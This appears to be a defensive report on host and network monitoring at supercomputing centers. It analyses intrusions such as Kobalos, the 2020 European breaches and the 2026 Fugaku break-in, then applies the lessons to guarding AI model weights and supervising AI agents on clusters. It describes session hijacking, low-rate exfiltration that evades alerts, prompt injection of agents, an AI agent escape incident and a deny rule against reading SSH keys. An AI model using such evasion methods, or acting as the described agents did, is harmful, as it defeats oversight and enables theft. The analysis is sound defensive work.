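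General server rules would normally cover these nodes, but centers publish little about what they run on them. *Managing HPC Security at LANL using Splunk and Nessus* (Shrader, 2024) describes the main security tools at Los Alamos. Nessus scans machines for known vulnerabilities, so staff can use it to find out that a management server needs a patch, but it doesn't replace monitoring what runs on the server.

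In March and May 2024, Lee listed Elastic Defend among products Livermore might explore. According to a customer story by Elastic, the laboratory already sent most of its data through Elastic Agent, the program to which Defend adds EDR, so it could have tried Defend on some machines without introducing a completely new agent. There is no public sign of whether it did.

### Compute nodes

Centers still seem to largely avoid commercial security agents on compute nodes. Argonne exempts these nodes outright, and UC San Diego allows exemptions for high-performance systems that an agent would slow.

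An exemption can still carry obligations. UC San Diego requires a system's owner to describe the effect on performance, propose other safeguards and state how long the exemption should last. Exempt systems need protections such as private networks, logging and restricted access, and someone has to monitor them manually. The school reviews each exemption every year and can revoke it if an attacker exploits the system. The yearly review forces staff to reconsider the performance argument as agents improve.

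Some substitutes limit what an account can do before anyone detects an intrusion. At MIT, new users get about two nodes, and staff observe their work before allowing them more, HPCwire reports. This limits the damage from a newly created account, but an intruder who steals an established researcher's credential gets the larger allowance. One operator at the 2023 workshop described users as a "human intrusion detection system" because they know how their programs normally perform and sometimes notice a problem before staff do.

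Government centers seem to be developing some of their own host monitoring. *HPC STX Outbrief* (Lee, 2025) summarizes a September 2025 meeting of about 60 security professionals from around 15 organizations. They discussed using auditd and two eBPF tools, Lintap and Panhandle, to record detailed events on hosts. Lee asks centers to share eBPF rules and audit settings and to work out which events are most valuable, but names no commercial EDR product. This suggests that buying an agent was not the group's main plan, though it is weak evidence about what the centers run. Lee also writes that "HPC is no longer out of scope", so centers may find it harder to leave compute nodes without an agent or a substitute.

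In April 2026, CSCS presented DenyRoot, a substitute for commercial agents that can respond as well as record. It uses eBPF to check when a process is about to change its user identity, for example to become root. If the change breaks the center's policy, DenyRoot can kill the user's sessions and processes and block further logins. Centers might otherwise buy this kind of response from an EDR vendor, but with DenyRoot they keep control of the policy. The tool cannot stop an attack that runs code inside the kernel, and such an attack could disable it. It also does not prevent attacks on flaws in programs that the center already allows to run as root.

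## What past intrusions show about detection

Overhead tests and simulated attacks show little about whether a center would notice a real intruder. Known intrusions are better evidence, although few centers publish full accounts of them.

NCSA's unusually long record includes forensic reports on 227 successful attacks between 2002 and 2022. Its investigators worked out how the attacker got in for 178 of them. NCSA's 2008 monitoring policy attributed a quarter of the incidents on its HPC systems to stolen credentials. The true share may have been higher, since logins with stolen credentials look normal.

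From 2018 to 2022, NCSA's network monitoring raised 115.6 million alerts, or about 79,000 a day. Investigators confirmed 11 successful attacks in the same period, roughly one for every 10.5 million alerts. Nobody can read 79,000 alerts a day, so software has to discard or combine nearly all of them first, and it may discard one about a real attack.

According to NCSA's *Preparations in Place*, part of its incident response plan, signs of an incident come primarily from the security team's own monitoring, and affected users report some incidents. Third parties are also a common source. They include REN-ISAC, which passes security warnings between research and education networks, and XSEDE, a program that shared supercomputers among US researchers. So NCSA regularly learned of intrusions from outsiders, even with an experienced security team and its own Zeek rules.

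### Stolen credentials that spread between sites

In spring 2004, attackers broke into research computers across the United States and Europe, including machines at US supercomputing centers. That April, Stanford University warned that the attackers were cracking or intercepting passwords, logging in as ordinary users and then exploiting known flaws to gain root. In 2009, a US grand jury indicted a Swedish man for intrusions at Cisco and at NASA, including its supercomputing division. He was 16 when the intrusions occurred.

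The attackers could use the same technique at each site because researchers had accounts at several centers and often used the same password for them. In *Credential wars*, Krous and Sharma (2011) describe a later, similar case and how staff reconstructed it.

| Record | What staff learned from it |
|---|---|
| Zeek alert | A server had downloaded C source code from a site that does not normally distribute software |
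| Network flows | At about the same time, an SSH connection arrived from an outside address and the server opened several file transfer connections |
| System log | A user had logged in from that address for the first time |
| Files on the server | The user's account owned a file that a known attack on udev, the Linux device manager, leaves behind |

Each record supplied information missing from the one before. The alert did not explain the download, and the flow record could not show whether the SSH login had succeeded or which account it used. Staff investigated further and found that the intruder had gained root and replaced the SSH server with a version that saved users' passwords to a file. The login from a new address came before the download but was weak evidence by itself. A rule combining the two could have alerted staff before they began searching by hand.

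In May 2020 the same kind of attack closed several European centers. The University of Edinburgh cut off access to ARCHER, then Britain's national supercomputer, on May 11 because of an exploit on its login nodes. Centers in Germany and Switzerland shut down systems within days. EGI, a federation of European research computing sites, reported that attackers were moving from one victim to the next with stolen SSH credentials. They used some of the machines to mine the cryptocurrency Monero, and at one site they mined only at night. A news report cited in *Understanding Cyber Threats Against the Universities, Colleges, and Schools* (2023) also attributes the Edinburgh shutdown to mining malware, though Edinburgh's early notices mentioned only the exploit.

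Investigators at several sites found two small hidden programs in the directory for font settings. One gave an ordinary user root access, and the other removed traces from the logs. Campbell's rule for unexpected switches to root would have been well suited to detecting the first. A center could have caught the second by comparing a node's login records with the copies in its central log store.

### Kobalos

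In February 2021 the security company ESET described Kobalos, a small backdoor it had found on research clusters and other machines. On most of the infected systems, the attackers had also installed an altered SSH client, which recorded the username, password and destination whenever someone connected to another computer. ESET did not determine how the attackers first got in or what they wanted, and it found no sign of cryptocurrency mining.

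One version of Kobalos ran inside the SSH server and waited for a connection from source port 55201. Any other connection received a normal login prompt. ESET used this behavior to search the internet for infected servers and notify their owners. Many of the victims learned about the intrusion from these notices, although they were not ESET customers.

Instrumented SSH would have been little help on such a server, since the backdoor took over before an ordinary session began. Zeek's connection log includes source ports, so a center that had kept its logs long enough could search them for the backdoor's source port once ESET had published the number. Linux clients normally choose from about 28,000 source ports, so at NERSC's 2011 rate of 52,000 logins a day, about two legitimate connections a day would match by chance, few enough for a person to check. Comparing the SSH programs with known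 correct copies could have detected Kobalos without the port number.

### Ten petabytes from Tianjin

On February 6, 2026, a seller called FlamingChina posted data samples on Telegram. The seller claimed to have more than 10 petabytes from the National Supercomputing Center in Tianjin, which serves over 6,000 clients, including Chinese defense agencies. CNN could not verify where the data came from, but several experts who examined the samples thought they looked genuine (Yee, *A hacker has allegedly breached one of China's supercomputers*).

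Someone claiming to be the hacker told Marc Hofer, a security researcher, that they had entered through a compromised VPN domain (a VPN gives outside users an encrypted route into a private network). The person said automated programs then copied the data out over about six months. The seller has a reason to exaggerate, so the total is doubtful even if the theft happened.

Still, the claimed rate is plausible. Moving 10 petabytes in six months requires an average of 5.1 gigabits per second, about 2.5 percent of the capacity of a single NERSC data transfer node. At the speed of ESnet's test between Marseille and San Diego, the transfer would take less than 12 days.

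Dakota Cary, a consultant at the security company SentinelOne, told CNN that the attacker seemed to have split the data among many servers so that no single transfer stood out. With 100 servers, each would have received about 51 megabits per second, less than many home internet connections can carry. A rule that flags large individual transfers would probably miss this.

The total, about 55 terabytes a day for six months, would be harder to hide. By comparing each account's outgoing data with its project's storage, a center could easily find an account that sent out far more than its project owned. To assign the traffic to accounts, the center would have to match Zeek's logs with host records, or with file system records of which account read which files. If the attacker used many accounts or had root, the totals for each account might still look ordinary.

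### Mining on Lengau

In late May 2026, intruders gained access to parts of Lengau, a supercomputer that South Africa's Centre for High Performance Computing opened in 2016, and installed cryptocurrency mining malware. In a written answer to parliament, science minister Blade Nzimande blamed vulnerabilities in the ageing system, some of whose components no longer had full vendor support (Mzekandaba, 2026, *Cause of breach on SA's supercomputer revealed*).

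The answer left out the facts most useful for studying detection: who noticed the miner, how long it had run, and which account or service the intruders used. Old hardware explains why breaking in was easier, but it does not prevent monitoring, since process accounting and auditd both predate Lengau by many years. Staff could have looked for busy processors with no matching job or, if the intruders submitted the miner as a normal job, for a miner's typical pattern of machine use.

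The center's planned improvements include monitoring for abnormal computing workloads and suspicious logins, which suggests that it had done too little to monitor for either. Specialists from another part of the same research council helped with the forensic analysis, and the center is having its new measures independently checked.

### Fugaku's public status page

Fugaku, in Kobe, is run by the Japanese research institute RIKEN and was once the world's fastest supercomputer. Intruders entered its operations network between November 10 and 13, 2026, starting from a public web page that displayed the machine's status. The timeline below follows RIKEN's first notice, as reported in 日本時事新聞's *スパコン「富岳」に不正アクセス、運用を停止 利用者4597人の情報や外部接続の鍵が流出の恐れ* (2026).

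| Time in Japan | What happened |
|---|---|
| November 10 | The intrusion begins |
| November 12 | RIKEN and its maintenance contractor notice suspicious traffic and investigate |
| November 13, 16:33 | RIKEN confirms the intrusion |
| November 13, 22:07 | RIKEN isolates the system the intruders came through |
| November 14, 04:30 | RIKEN stops normal operation and blocks outside access |
| November 14, 20:20 | RIKEN replaces the administrators' keys |
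| November 15, 10:51 | RIKEN informs the institutions in HPCI, Japan's network of shared research computers |
| November 15, 16:18 | RIKEN emails users, stops all jobs and disables every user's login key |

Press accounts disagree about the first days. Jiji Press' *利用者の個人情報流出か＝理研、スパコン「富岳」など* says the contractor noticed the traffic on November 12. Antena 3's *A fost atacat supercomputerul Japoniei*, which relays the Japanese broadcaster NHK, says the traffic was on the user authentication system. Udinmwen (2026), in *Japanese supercomputer hit by suspected cyberattack*, describes a November 13 attempt to log in with stolen credentials, after which RIKEN immediately cut the machine off. RIKEN's own times are more reliable and show almost 12 hours between the confirmation and the shutdown, although RIKEN had isolated the entry point in between. Jobs could continue for another day and a half.

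RIKEN first listed fixing a software vulnerability among its remedies. But on December 3 it told a government committee that the intruders had exploited a combination of individual settings, according to GameBusiness.jp's *「富岳」不正アクセス、原因は脆弱性ではなく「設定の組み合わせ」* (2026). No patch would have kept them out, and a scanner that looks for missing patches would presumably have found nothing.

The intruders operated several internal servers and planted or changed scripts on some of them. They accessed the contact details of 4,222 Fugaku users and possibly the names and email addresses of up to 375 users of another RIKEN machine. They also collected 430 SSH private keys and similar credentials from users' home directories. RIKEN has found no specific evidence that research results leaked, but it says the intruders may have taken users' research files.

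日本時事新聞's *富岳不正アクセス、住所や電話番号も漏えい前提に 理研が第2報、外部接続の鍵430件* (2026) reports that RIKEN found much of this by going back through its logs with AI tools. Useful evidence had therefore reached the logs, and some of it might have triggered an alert earlier. Three kinds of record seem most promising:

- The server behind a status page normally runs a handful of programs and contacts a few known machines. A new program or a connection to an unfamiliar management server would be much more suspicious there than on a login node.
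- Audit records of file access could show one process reading private keys from many users' home directories. Backup software does this too, so staff would have to exempt it.
- A comparison of system scripts with known correct copies could reveal the ones the intruders had changed.

A monitor at the network border might miss the internal connection from the web server to the management servers. Instrumented SSH would have missed the entry because it did not involve an SSH login. The intruders reached the operations network without first taking over an ordinary account on a login node, which supports NIST's advice to log management servers in the most detail.

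Katsunari Yoshioka, a professor at Yokohama National University, questioned whether RIKEN had properly separated its key internal systems from those open to the internet. 凤凰网's *日本顶级超算“富岳”遭入侵，4597人信息或遭泄露* (2026), citing Nikkei Asia, adds that about 13 billion of Fugaku's 14 billion yen in annual operating costs goes to electricity, utilities and other operations. RIKEN acknowledged that it spends relatively little on security. More money might have helped, but separating a public web page from the management network depends mainly on design.

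### Who raised the alarm

The table compares these cases with a 2010 break-in at Berkeley Lab and a breach of a University of Tokyo server that managed accounts for HPCI. 東京大学情報基盤センター's *東京大学管理の HPCI 機材への不正アクセスについて* (2021) discloses the Tokyo breach.

| Intrusion | Entry | Time to discovery | What revealed it | Record that might have shown it sooner |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Research sites, 2004 | Stolen passwords | Varied by site | Varied by site | Logins from new addresses, followed by a switch to root |
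| Berkeley Lab cluster, 2010 | A user's open SSH session | Not published | Not published | Commands typed in the session |
| European centers, May 2020 | Stolen SSH credentials | Varied by site | An exploit on login nodes, at Edinburgh | A process becoming root through a hidden program |
| Kobalos, made public in 2021 | Unknown | Unknown | ESET's research | Changed SSH programs |
| University of Tokyo, 2021 | Not published | Up to about 20 days | Not published | Administrator logins, copied to another machine |
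| Tianjin, 2026 (alleged) | VPN | Six months or more | The seller's own samples | Outgoing data added up by account |
| Lengau, 2026 | Flaws in old components | Not published | Not published | Busy processors with no matching job |
| Fugaku, 2026 | Public status page | Two to three days | Suspicious traffic | Connections from the web server to management servers |

The table has gaps because centers rarely explain which log or person exposed an intruder. They usually disclose what the intruder took and what users should do, because the law and their users require it. Without the detection details, other centers can't tell which kind of monitoring to invest in.

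The Fugaku intrusion was discovered faster than any other with a published discovery time, but the intruders still had two days before anyone noticed unusual traffic. Copying 430 small key files takes seconds, so faster detection would probably have come too late to protect the keys, though it could have limited what the intruders did next.

The last column also benefits from hindsight. Each suggested record would have been one of many, and nobody has tested how often the matching rule would raise false alarms at these centers.

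### Warning the next center

Users keep private keys on one supercomputer so they can connect to others. 理化学研究所計算科学研究センター's *スーパーコンピュータ「富岳」セキュリティホワイトペーパー* (2021) makes users responsible for their own accounts and credentials, and RIKEN responsible for the network and the system software. The 2026 breach involved both areas of responsibility. The intruders got in through RIKEN's network, and 233 of the 430 keys had no passphrase, so anyone who copied them could use them immediately. A passphrase protects each of the other 197 only as long as nobody guesses it.

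The intruders tried some of the stolen credentials on other systems. RIKEN has not named these systems or said whether any attempt succeeded. It warned the other HPCI institutions about 42 hours after confirming the intrusion, and users about five hours later. Until they were warned, centers that did not know of the breach would have accepted the stolen keys as genuine. Disabling login keys at Fugaku could not prevent their use elsewhere, because only the system receiving a key can refuse it.

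A warning is most useful if it contains something the receiving center can search for. An SSH server can log a fingerprint, a short code that identifies the key used to log in. A center that knows which private keys intruders copied can usually calculate the matching fingerprints and send them to other sites without revealing the keys. Those sites can then block the keys and check whether anyone has already used them. RIKEN contacted the affected users individually and asked them to have their keys disabled elsewhere. How quickly this works depends on when users read their email.

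The 2021 Tokyo breach exposed a different route between the same centers. Someone gained administrator access to a temporary server that held about 400 HPCI usernames with encrypted passwords. The affected period was September 15 to October 5, and the university published its notice ten days later. An attacker can test guesses against encrypted passwords on their own computer, where no center can record the attempts.

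General warnings are less useful for detection than specific ones. On November 5, 2026, Japan's National Cybersecurity Office told organizations to check what they exposed to the internet, because attackers were scanning public websites on a large scale, probably with the help of AI. The Fugaku intrusion began five days later. The advice was highly relevant to that intrusion, but it gave RIKEN no particular address or program to look for.

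Krous and Sharma recommend that centers share information with trusted peers and make a stolen account less useful for finding new targets. If a center hashes the names in SSH's list of visited servers, an intruder has to guess where the user has accounts, and wrong guesses create failed connections that Zeek can detect.

### What multi-factor login changed

Stronger login requirements appear to have prevented many intrusions at NCSA. Its investigators confirmed 11 attacks from 2018 to 2022, or fewer than three a year. The other 216 reports cover about 16 years, an average of 13 or 14 a year. Compromises fell markedly after 2011, and researchers who studied the reports credit measures such as two-factor login. But NCSA also made other changes over those years, and attackers may have moved to easier targets, so it is hard to say how much of the fall is due to login security.

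By October 2010, Berkeley Lab had moved around 1,000 users to one-time passwords over three years, largely to stop credential theft. That month, intruders still broke into a cluster that required them and replaced its SSH server. Staff found a long-running SSH connection from a university computer and traced it back. Zeek logs at the university showed that someone had downloaded a tool of about 70 lines of C code, which had been public since February 2000.

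With root access on the researcher's computer, the intruder could use the tool to hijack a session that the researcher had already opened with a valid one-time password. The intruder could not see the output, but a single command to download and run a script would be enough. The researcher might see the command appear on the screen and not understand it.

Krous and Sharma had no good defense against this method, because the intruder had gained root on a machine outside the laboratory's control, but they found that ending SSH sessions after a set time helps. Centers that never make users reauthenticate, as NIST's draft overlay allows, give intruders more time to use this method.

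Multi-factor login is better at stopping a breach from spreading than at preventing the initial breach. When the Fugaku intrusion became public, Kyoto University quickly decided to turn on multi-factor login for its supercomputer, so that a key stolen from Fugaku would not be enough to get in. Multi-factor login would not have kept the intruders out of Fugaku itself, because they came through a web page and did not need a user's login. NERSC's temporary keys offer similar protection, because a key left on another supercomputer soon expires.

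These changes make the remaining intrusions harder to detect from login records. Once a center blocks most stolen passwords, a larger share of its intrusions will come through hijacked sessions, web services and flaws in its own configuration. The authentication log may then look normal or contain no login at all, so records of processes, file access and internal connections become more important.

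### Intrusions nobody found

Every case here was both noticed and made public. Miners are relatively easy to notice because they use processors that researchers are waiting for, and a seller of stolen data has to advertise. An intruder who quietly copies one group's results once a month neither ties up processors nor advertises, so such cases are probably underrepresented in the record. If the Tianjin data is genuine, no one outside the center would have known about the theft had the thief kept the data.

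A center can roughly estimate how many intrusions it misses if it has two independent sources of detection. Suppose its own monitoring finds 8 intrusions in some period, outsiders report 4, and 2 appear on both lists. Its monitoring found half of the intrusions that outsiders reported. If it also found half of all intrusions, there were 16 in total. The two lists contain 10 different intrusions, so about 6 remain undiscovered.

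Biologists estimate animal populations in the same way, by marking some animals and counting how many turn up in a second catch. The method assumes that being on one list makes an intrusion no more or less likely to be on the other. That is doubtful here because a careful intruder tends to escape notice by both the center and outsiders, so the true number would be higher than the estimate. With only 2 cases on both lists, one more or one fewer would also change the estimate a great deal. A center can still attempt the calculation if it records who raised each alarm.

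## Which practices carry over to AI training clusters

An intruder who wants a research group's results may have to return every month for new ones, but one who wants an AI company's model may need to copy it only once. A trained model consists mainly of its weights, the numbers set during training. Anthropic's *Activating AI Safety Level 3 Protections* (2025) explains that a thief who has the weights can run the model on other machines, without the company's monitoring and safeguards.

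AI companies train models on clusters that closely resemble supercomputers, and Guo and colleagues list AI training among the uses that NIST's overlay covers. On a university's AI cluster, where students share login nodes and run their own code, the practices of supercomputing centers should carry over almost unchanged. A company that trains its own models differs more from a supercomputing center than a university does.

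### How the two kinds of cluster differ

| | Supercomputing center | AI company's training cluster |
|---|---|---|
| Users | Thousands of outside researchers | Screened employees and contractors, and AI agents |
| Login path | SSH from almost any computer | Usually a company laptop, then SSH or a web-based control system |
| Starting jobs | A scheduler such as Slurm | Slurm or Kubernetes |
| Shared storage | Files of many unrelated projects | Training data and model files of one company |
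| Synchronized jobs | Some, of all sizes | A few very large ones, beside many experiments |
| Value of one stolen file | Usually limited to one project | Possibly a whole model |
| Security budget | Competes with computing for money | Larger; 5.2 percent of Anthropic's staff worked in security or related roles in May 2025 |
| Who may change the software | Any user can compile and run a program | Researchers, but the company can forbid it near the weights |

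Kubernetes is an open-source system that starts programs in containers on many machines and restarts them when they fail. It does much of what a scheduler does, but it leaves different records.

Most of these differences make monitoring easier. A company can issue its users' laptops and decide which programs they run. It also knows its users and can dismiss anyone who ignores the rules.

The value of the file has the opposite effect, because it attracts much stronger attackers. *SL5 Standard for AI Security*, a first draft by Thiergart, Tzfati and colleagues (2026), describes protections against operations comparable to 1,000 experts working for years with up to $1 billion. SL5 stands for Security Level 5, the highest level in a 2024 report by the research organization RAND. The protections that Anthropic described in 2025 are meant to stop criminal groups, corporate spies and ordinary insiders,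 but not governments that specifically target the company.

### How quickly a model file can leave

At 5 gigabits a second, about the average rate claimed for the Tianjin theft, a thief could copy a 2-terabyte model file out of a cluster in about 53 minutes. RIKEN's staff noticed the Fugaku intrusion after two to three days, and two days is long enough to copy that file 54 times at the same rate.

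Detection that takes days can still help a company find out which account the thief used and what else is missing, but it cannot prevent the loss. Even a much faster response could be too slow. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) describes monitoring of AI models that aims to alert staff within 30 minutes of surfacing a concern. For the most serious alerts, staff have another 30 minutes to establish that the alarm is false before they are expected to pause the activity. If a theft continued for that full hour, the thief would have the whole file.

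The company therefore has to limit how fast data can leave.

| Limit on all outgoing data | Time for 2 terabytes to leave | Comparison with known intrusions |
|---|---|---|
| 5 gigabits a second | 53 minutes | Far shorter than any published time to discovery |
| 100 megabits a second | 44 hours | Slightly shorter than at Fugaku |
| 10 megabits a second | 18.5 days | Slightly shorter than the maximum at the University of Tokyo |
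| 1 megabit a second | 185 days | About as long as the alleged copying at Tianjin |

If outbound traffic is limited to 10 megabits a second, a practice that finds an intruder in three days can still help prevent theft of a model, because most of the weight file will not have left the cluster. The limit has to apply to all network exits combined, or the thief can divide the file among them. It also has to be well below the rate that the full file size would suggest, because a thief might store each weight with a quarter of the original bits, which makes the model somewhat worse but cuts the copying time to a quarter.

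Thiergart and colleagues want hardware to enforce the limit, so that it holds "even if attempts go undetected". Their draft does not set the number. The limit also works only if the weights are much larger than anything the protected machines need to send out. That is plausible for a model that answers in text, since 10 megabits a second still allows 1.25 megabytes of text each second. The limit is a serious problem for a company that trains one model at several sites, because the draft requires transfers above it to travel on encrypted physical media. Thiergart and colleagues concede that such training may prove infeasible.

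Anthropic had preliminary limits on outbound data in May 2025. It expected to lower them over time until stealing the weights before anyone noticed would be very difficult. It reports that setting the limits also improved detection, because staff had to learn how data was leaving its systems.

A research center could hardly cap transfer speeds this way, because its users need to transfer large files. The cap also doesn't protect everything an AI company owns. A collection of training code might be only 100 megabytes, which would take 80 seconds to transfer at 10 megabits a second. For secrets that small, access controls and monitoring inside the machines matter more.

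### Sessions and processes

Session recording carries over wherever employees still type commands. They probably do this mostly on machines used for research and debugging, where the sessions would look much like those on a login node. The SL5 draft prohibits interactive coding on the machines that hold the weights and requires programmers to have their code tested and signed before it runs there. A shell on such a machine would be unusual enough to justify an alert by itself. These sessions would be rare, so the company could also keep all of their output, whereas NERSC's server by default copies only the first lines after each input.

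But an instrumented SSH server would miss some of these sessions, because Kubernetes lets staff open a shell inside a container through its own control server, without using SSH on the node. The company would have to record those sessions at the control server or inside the container, where an intruder could more easily tamper with the record.

Anthropic's approval procedure could make the recordings more useful. An employee who needs access to the weights must authenticate with a physical security key, give a reason and get time-limited approval from a second person. Staff could compare each session with the reason given for it. If someone asked for access to fix a loading error and then started an upload, the mismatch would be much stronger evidence of misuse than the upload alone.

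Consent is simpler in one way, since employees can be told about the monitoring when they are hired. But labor and privacy law may restrict the monitoring itself. Thiergart and colleagues list as an open question whether companies in states such as California and Illinois can monitor staff as closely as the paper proposes.

Process records should transfer even better than session recordings because a company, unlike a supercomputing center, can list the approved programs for the machines that hold the weights. An execution record for any other program would mean either that the block on unapproved programs had failed or that someone had forgotten to update the list. Such records should be rare, and each is worth investigating.

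Containers make it harder to tell who started a program. Auditd records the identity a user logged in with and keeps it even if the user switches to root. Kubernetes starts containers without a login, so this field is normally empty, and many containers may run under the same service account. Each process record therefore also needs the container's identifier, so that staff can search the Kubernetes records for who requested the container.

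A list of approved programs doesn't prevent misuse of those programs. Thiergart and colleagues warn that an attacker could combine permitted operations into a sequence that leaks data, in which case the process records would contain only approved programs. They suggest having firmware check that operations run in an approved order, or permitting only larger units of code that someone has verified as a whole.

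### Light probes on training nodes

A training job divides its work among many GPUs, which have to exchange results before they continue, so the argument about small delays applies here too. A training step may last several seconds, and by the earlier calculation long steps lose little time. But the GPUs also exchange data many times within a step, so the real loss could be greater. A company should measure the loss on a full-size job before relying on an eight-node test.

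Two features of training favor eBPF probes. GPUs do most of the arithmetic, so the CPUs may have more spare capacity than they had in Wilson's benchmark. Model files are also few and very large. Houssel and colleagues found that recording tens of thousands of new files added a lot of overhead, but a probe that reports only who opens a model file would run rarely. If only the training job and one backup program are expected to read the model files, access by anything else should trigger an alert. A similar probe on the training data could add a lot of overhead if the data consists of millions of small files.

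The strictest designs make accelerators (GPUs or similar chips) harder to monitor from the host. Under the SL5 draft, weights arrive encrypted, and only the accelerator decrypts them. The accelerator denies the host access to its memory, so an intruder with root on the node could not read the weights there, but the company's monitoring software on that node could not inspect the memory either.

Some of the evidence would instead come from attestation, in which the chip sends a signed statement of its identity and the firmware it started with. The draft requires continuous checks of these statements and a log that reveals tampering. Attestation can show that a chip started with authorized firmware, but not what an employee did with access to it. Current hardware also falls short of the design. Nvidia's Blackwell chips, for example, rely on a protected area of the host's processor for part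 of this isolation.

### Network records and central logs

Matching host records with network records is likely to work better on a training cluster than on a login node, because a training node normally runs one job and has few reasons to contact the internet. OpenAI's *Frontier Governance Framework* describes running models in sandboxes, or restricted environments, that limit outgoing connections by default. Under such a rule, even a blocked attempt shows that a program tried to reach something it should not need.

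Matching a connection to the program behind it requires new data under Kubernetes, which gives groups of containers their own network addresses and can soon reuse them. Staff need to know which containers were using the address when the connection was made. A company that rents its machines from a cloud provider usually cannot install an optical tap and may have to rely on the provider's traffic summaries, which contain less detail than Zeek's logs. As on a supercomputer, direct memory transfers between nodes can escape both kinds of monitoring.

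Central logging carries over, but the log store should move inside the protected training cluster. Logs sent outside the cluster can be used to steal data, because an intruder who controls a node could hide pieces of the model weights in log records.

The logs would also take up permitted bandwidth that legitimate output needs. The parallel job described earlier, which produced 320,000 audit records from one command, would generate 160 megabytes of logs if each record took 500 bytes. With a limit of 10 megabits a second, sending them would take up the whole connection for more than two minutes. It makes more sense to keep the full logs on separate servers inside the protected area, analyze them there and send out only alerts.

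### Where a full security agent fits

Commercial security agents suit an AI company's laptops, login nodes and management servers, where a short delay affects few people. Before installing an agent on nodes that run synchronized training, the company should show that it does not slow the job. Argonne made the same distinction between its login nodes and compute nodes.

A vendor's cloud console is a more serious obstacle near the weights, because it needs a connection out of the cluster. Under the SL5 draft, the network is entirely separate from outside networks, which would rule the console out. The vendor would have to supply a version that the company can run itself, and staff would have to test and sign updates before installing them on machines that hold the weights.

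### What laboratories publish about host monitoring

Anthropic's 2025 report gives the most detail on monitoring tools, but little of it concerns training nodes. The report describes more than 100 new controls, including central logging with automated analysis, alerts for suspicious activity, network intrusion detection and honeypots, which are decoy systems meant to attract intruders. Anthropic runs EDR software and blocks unapproved programs on "Anthropic devices", mainly to protect employees' computers. The report does not state whether training nodes have a security agent, auditd or eBPF probes.

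OpenAI's framework is even more general. It lists encryption of unreleased weights, continuous monitoring, approval by several people, detailed logging and internal monitoring for anomalous activity, but does not name a method for recording what happens on a host.

In August 2026, after its AI agents broke out of a test and attacked the company Hugging Face, OpenAI published more about its research clusters. It had paused runs in which models could execute code or use tools with internet access, then checked each type of work before letting it resume. It now requires stronger isolation for code that models write. The network controls should hold even if an attacker compromises one program or supporting service. OpenAI was also improving how it collects and monitors security logs, which suggests that its earlier logging had gaps. It does not list the events it records on each node.

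The SL5 draft contains no controls from NIST's audit and accountability family, the part of the general catalog that covers log records, and it does not specify which process records a company should keep. It mentions system monitoring only as an addition to the outbound limit. These gaps exist because the first version covers only measures that take years to prepare, such as buildings and chips. Thiergart and colleagues expect to add most controls from existing high-security standards later.

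AI companies have a reason to withhold details, since attackers who knew the alert rules could avoid triggering them. A company's not publishing details is therefore only weak evidence that it records nothing. NERSC was open about its session recording and still caught intruders afterwards. An AI company could probably publish which types of event it records on training nodes, and what the recording costs, without revealing its rules. Outsiders currently cannot compare companies on either point.

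### AI agents as users

AI agents now use both kinds of cluster. In July 2026, OpenAI's agents ran commands on the company's research computers. At supercomputing centers, researchers use agents to write code, examine failed jobs and submit new ones. The centers record this work under the researcher's account.

Centers have adopted very different rules:

- NERSC generally lets users start AI agents on login nodes, with the user's own permissions. It recommends a mode in which the AI agent can change files only in its working directory.
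- NCAR's *Using Agentic Coding Assistants*, from the US National Center for Atmospheric Research, accepts light use on login nodes but tells users not to let the software run commands without approval.
- ALCF's *AI Guidance*, from Argonne's supercomputing facility, allows AI agents but recommends compute nodes. A fixed limit on each user's processes and threads applies on the login nodes.
- Clemson University bans AI coding assistants from its login nodes, and the Kempner Institute's *Using Agentic AI on the Cluster* does the same for AI agents on an AI research cluster at Harvard.
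- The University of Arizona's *Policy on the Use of Artificial Intelligence Agents and Autonomous Workflows* prohibits AI agents anywhere on its systems from acting repeatedly without a person approving each action.

These policies commonly make the user responsible for whatever the AI agent does, but they don't help staff tell from a log whether the researcher, an AI agent or an intruder gave a command.

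One difficulty is that an AI agent can issue commands faster than its user can read them, as Purdue University's RCAC warns in *Acceptable Use & Etiquette*. If 100 users each had an agent that ran 2,000 commands a day, a detector that wrongly flagged 0.1 percent of commands would raise 200 additional false alarms a day, three times as many as for the entire cluster that Ermopoulos and Yurcik studied.

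Other rules fail because they assume that somebody is typing. A user can type one sentence to an AI agent on the login node and leave the agent to work for an hour. Under NERSC's default capture limits, the session log may then contain only that sentence and the first few lines of the result. Detectors that recognize a person's typing rhythm would have nothing to measure while the agent works. Auditd can still record the agent's commands because they start as separate processes.

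An AI agent that runs on the user's laptop and sends commands to the center over SSH may open connections without a terminal. In Campbell's textbook case, a shell without a terminal was the first sign of the attack. NERSC warns that an agent connecting from the user's laptop over SSH looks like the user and bypasses the safeguards it has set up for AI agents on Perlmutter.

AI agents can also behave like an intruder exploring the system. NCAR notes that they often search the file tree to orient themselves, which can slow shared storage if they start too high up. A rule that flags any account reading widely across other people's directories would catch some of these searches. Similarly, ALCF says that if an AI agent keeps retrying a failed connection to another Argonne system, automatic network defenses may block SSH from the whole login node until someone with the right access removes the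 block.

Rules that flag specific acts carry over better. An unprivileged process that becomes root through an unknown program is suspicious whether a person or an AI agent started it. The same is true of a program that reads private keys from many home directories.

AI agents also let attackers in without a stolen credential. LUMI's *AI agent guide* warns that a web page or code repository can contain hidden instructions that take over an AI agent, a technique called prompt injection. The login, the account and the source address would then all be genuine, as in a hijacked SSH session. LUMI also forbids giving a password or key to an AI agent on a third party's system, which it treats as credential sharing. Enforcing this rule may help detection, because a login from an AI provider's data center would then be either a violation or an intrusion.

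The University of Southern California has built a record specifically for AI agents. CARC's *AI Coding Agents* (2026) describes how its research computing center controls two common programs, Claude Code and Codex:

1. The AI agent reads a file of local rules, such as which work belongs on compute nodes. This is only guidance.
2. Fixed settings deny some actions, such as reading private SSH keys, and require the user's approval for others. Root owns the settings, so users cannot loosen them.
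3. Before each shell command or file action, a script examines the proposal and allows it, blocks it or asks the user. It writes every decision to an audit log.

This log includes actions that the script blocked, which don't appear in process records because they never ran. The center tested the script with hundreds of artificial requests, then tested the AI agents in more than 60 real scenarios on the cluster. However, a user can install a separate copy of the program that ignores the script, and CARC acknowledges that a firm boundary also needs network and credential controls. Staff could look for such copies by searching process records for AI agents with no entries in the audit log.

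Process records can also help separate the AI agent's work from the user's. Auditd logs each process's parent, so staff can often trace a command back to the AI agent's program and apply different thresholds to it. The University of Arizona needs a method like this to enforce its policy, which lets staff stop any process that looks like an unsupervised AI agent before they know what the user intended. The policy also warns that an AI agent's actions can be hard to reconstruct after an incident.

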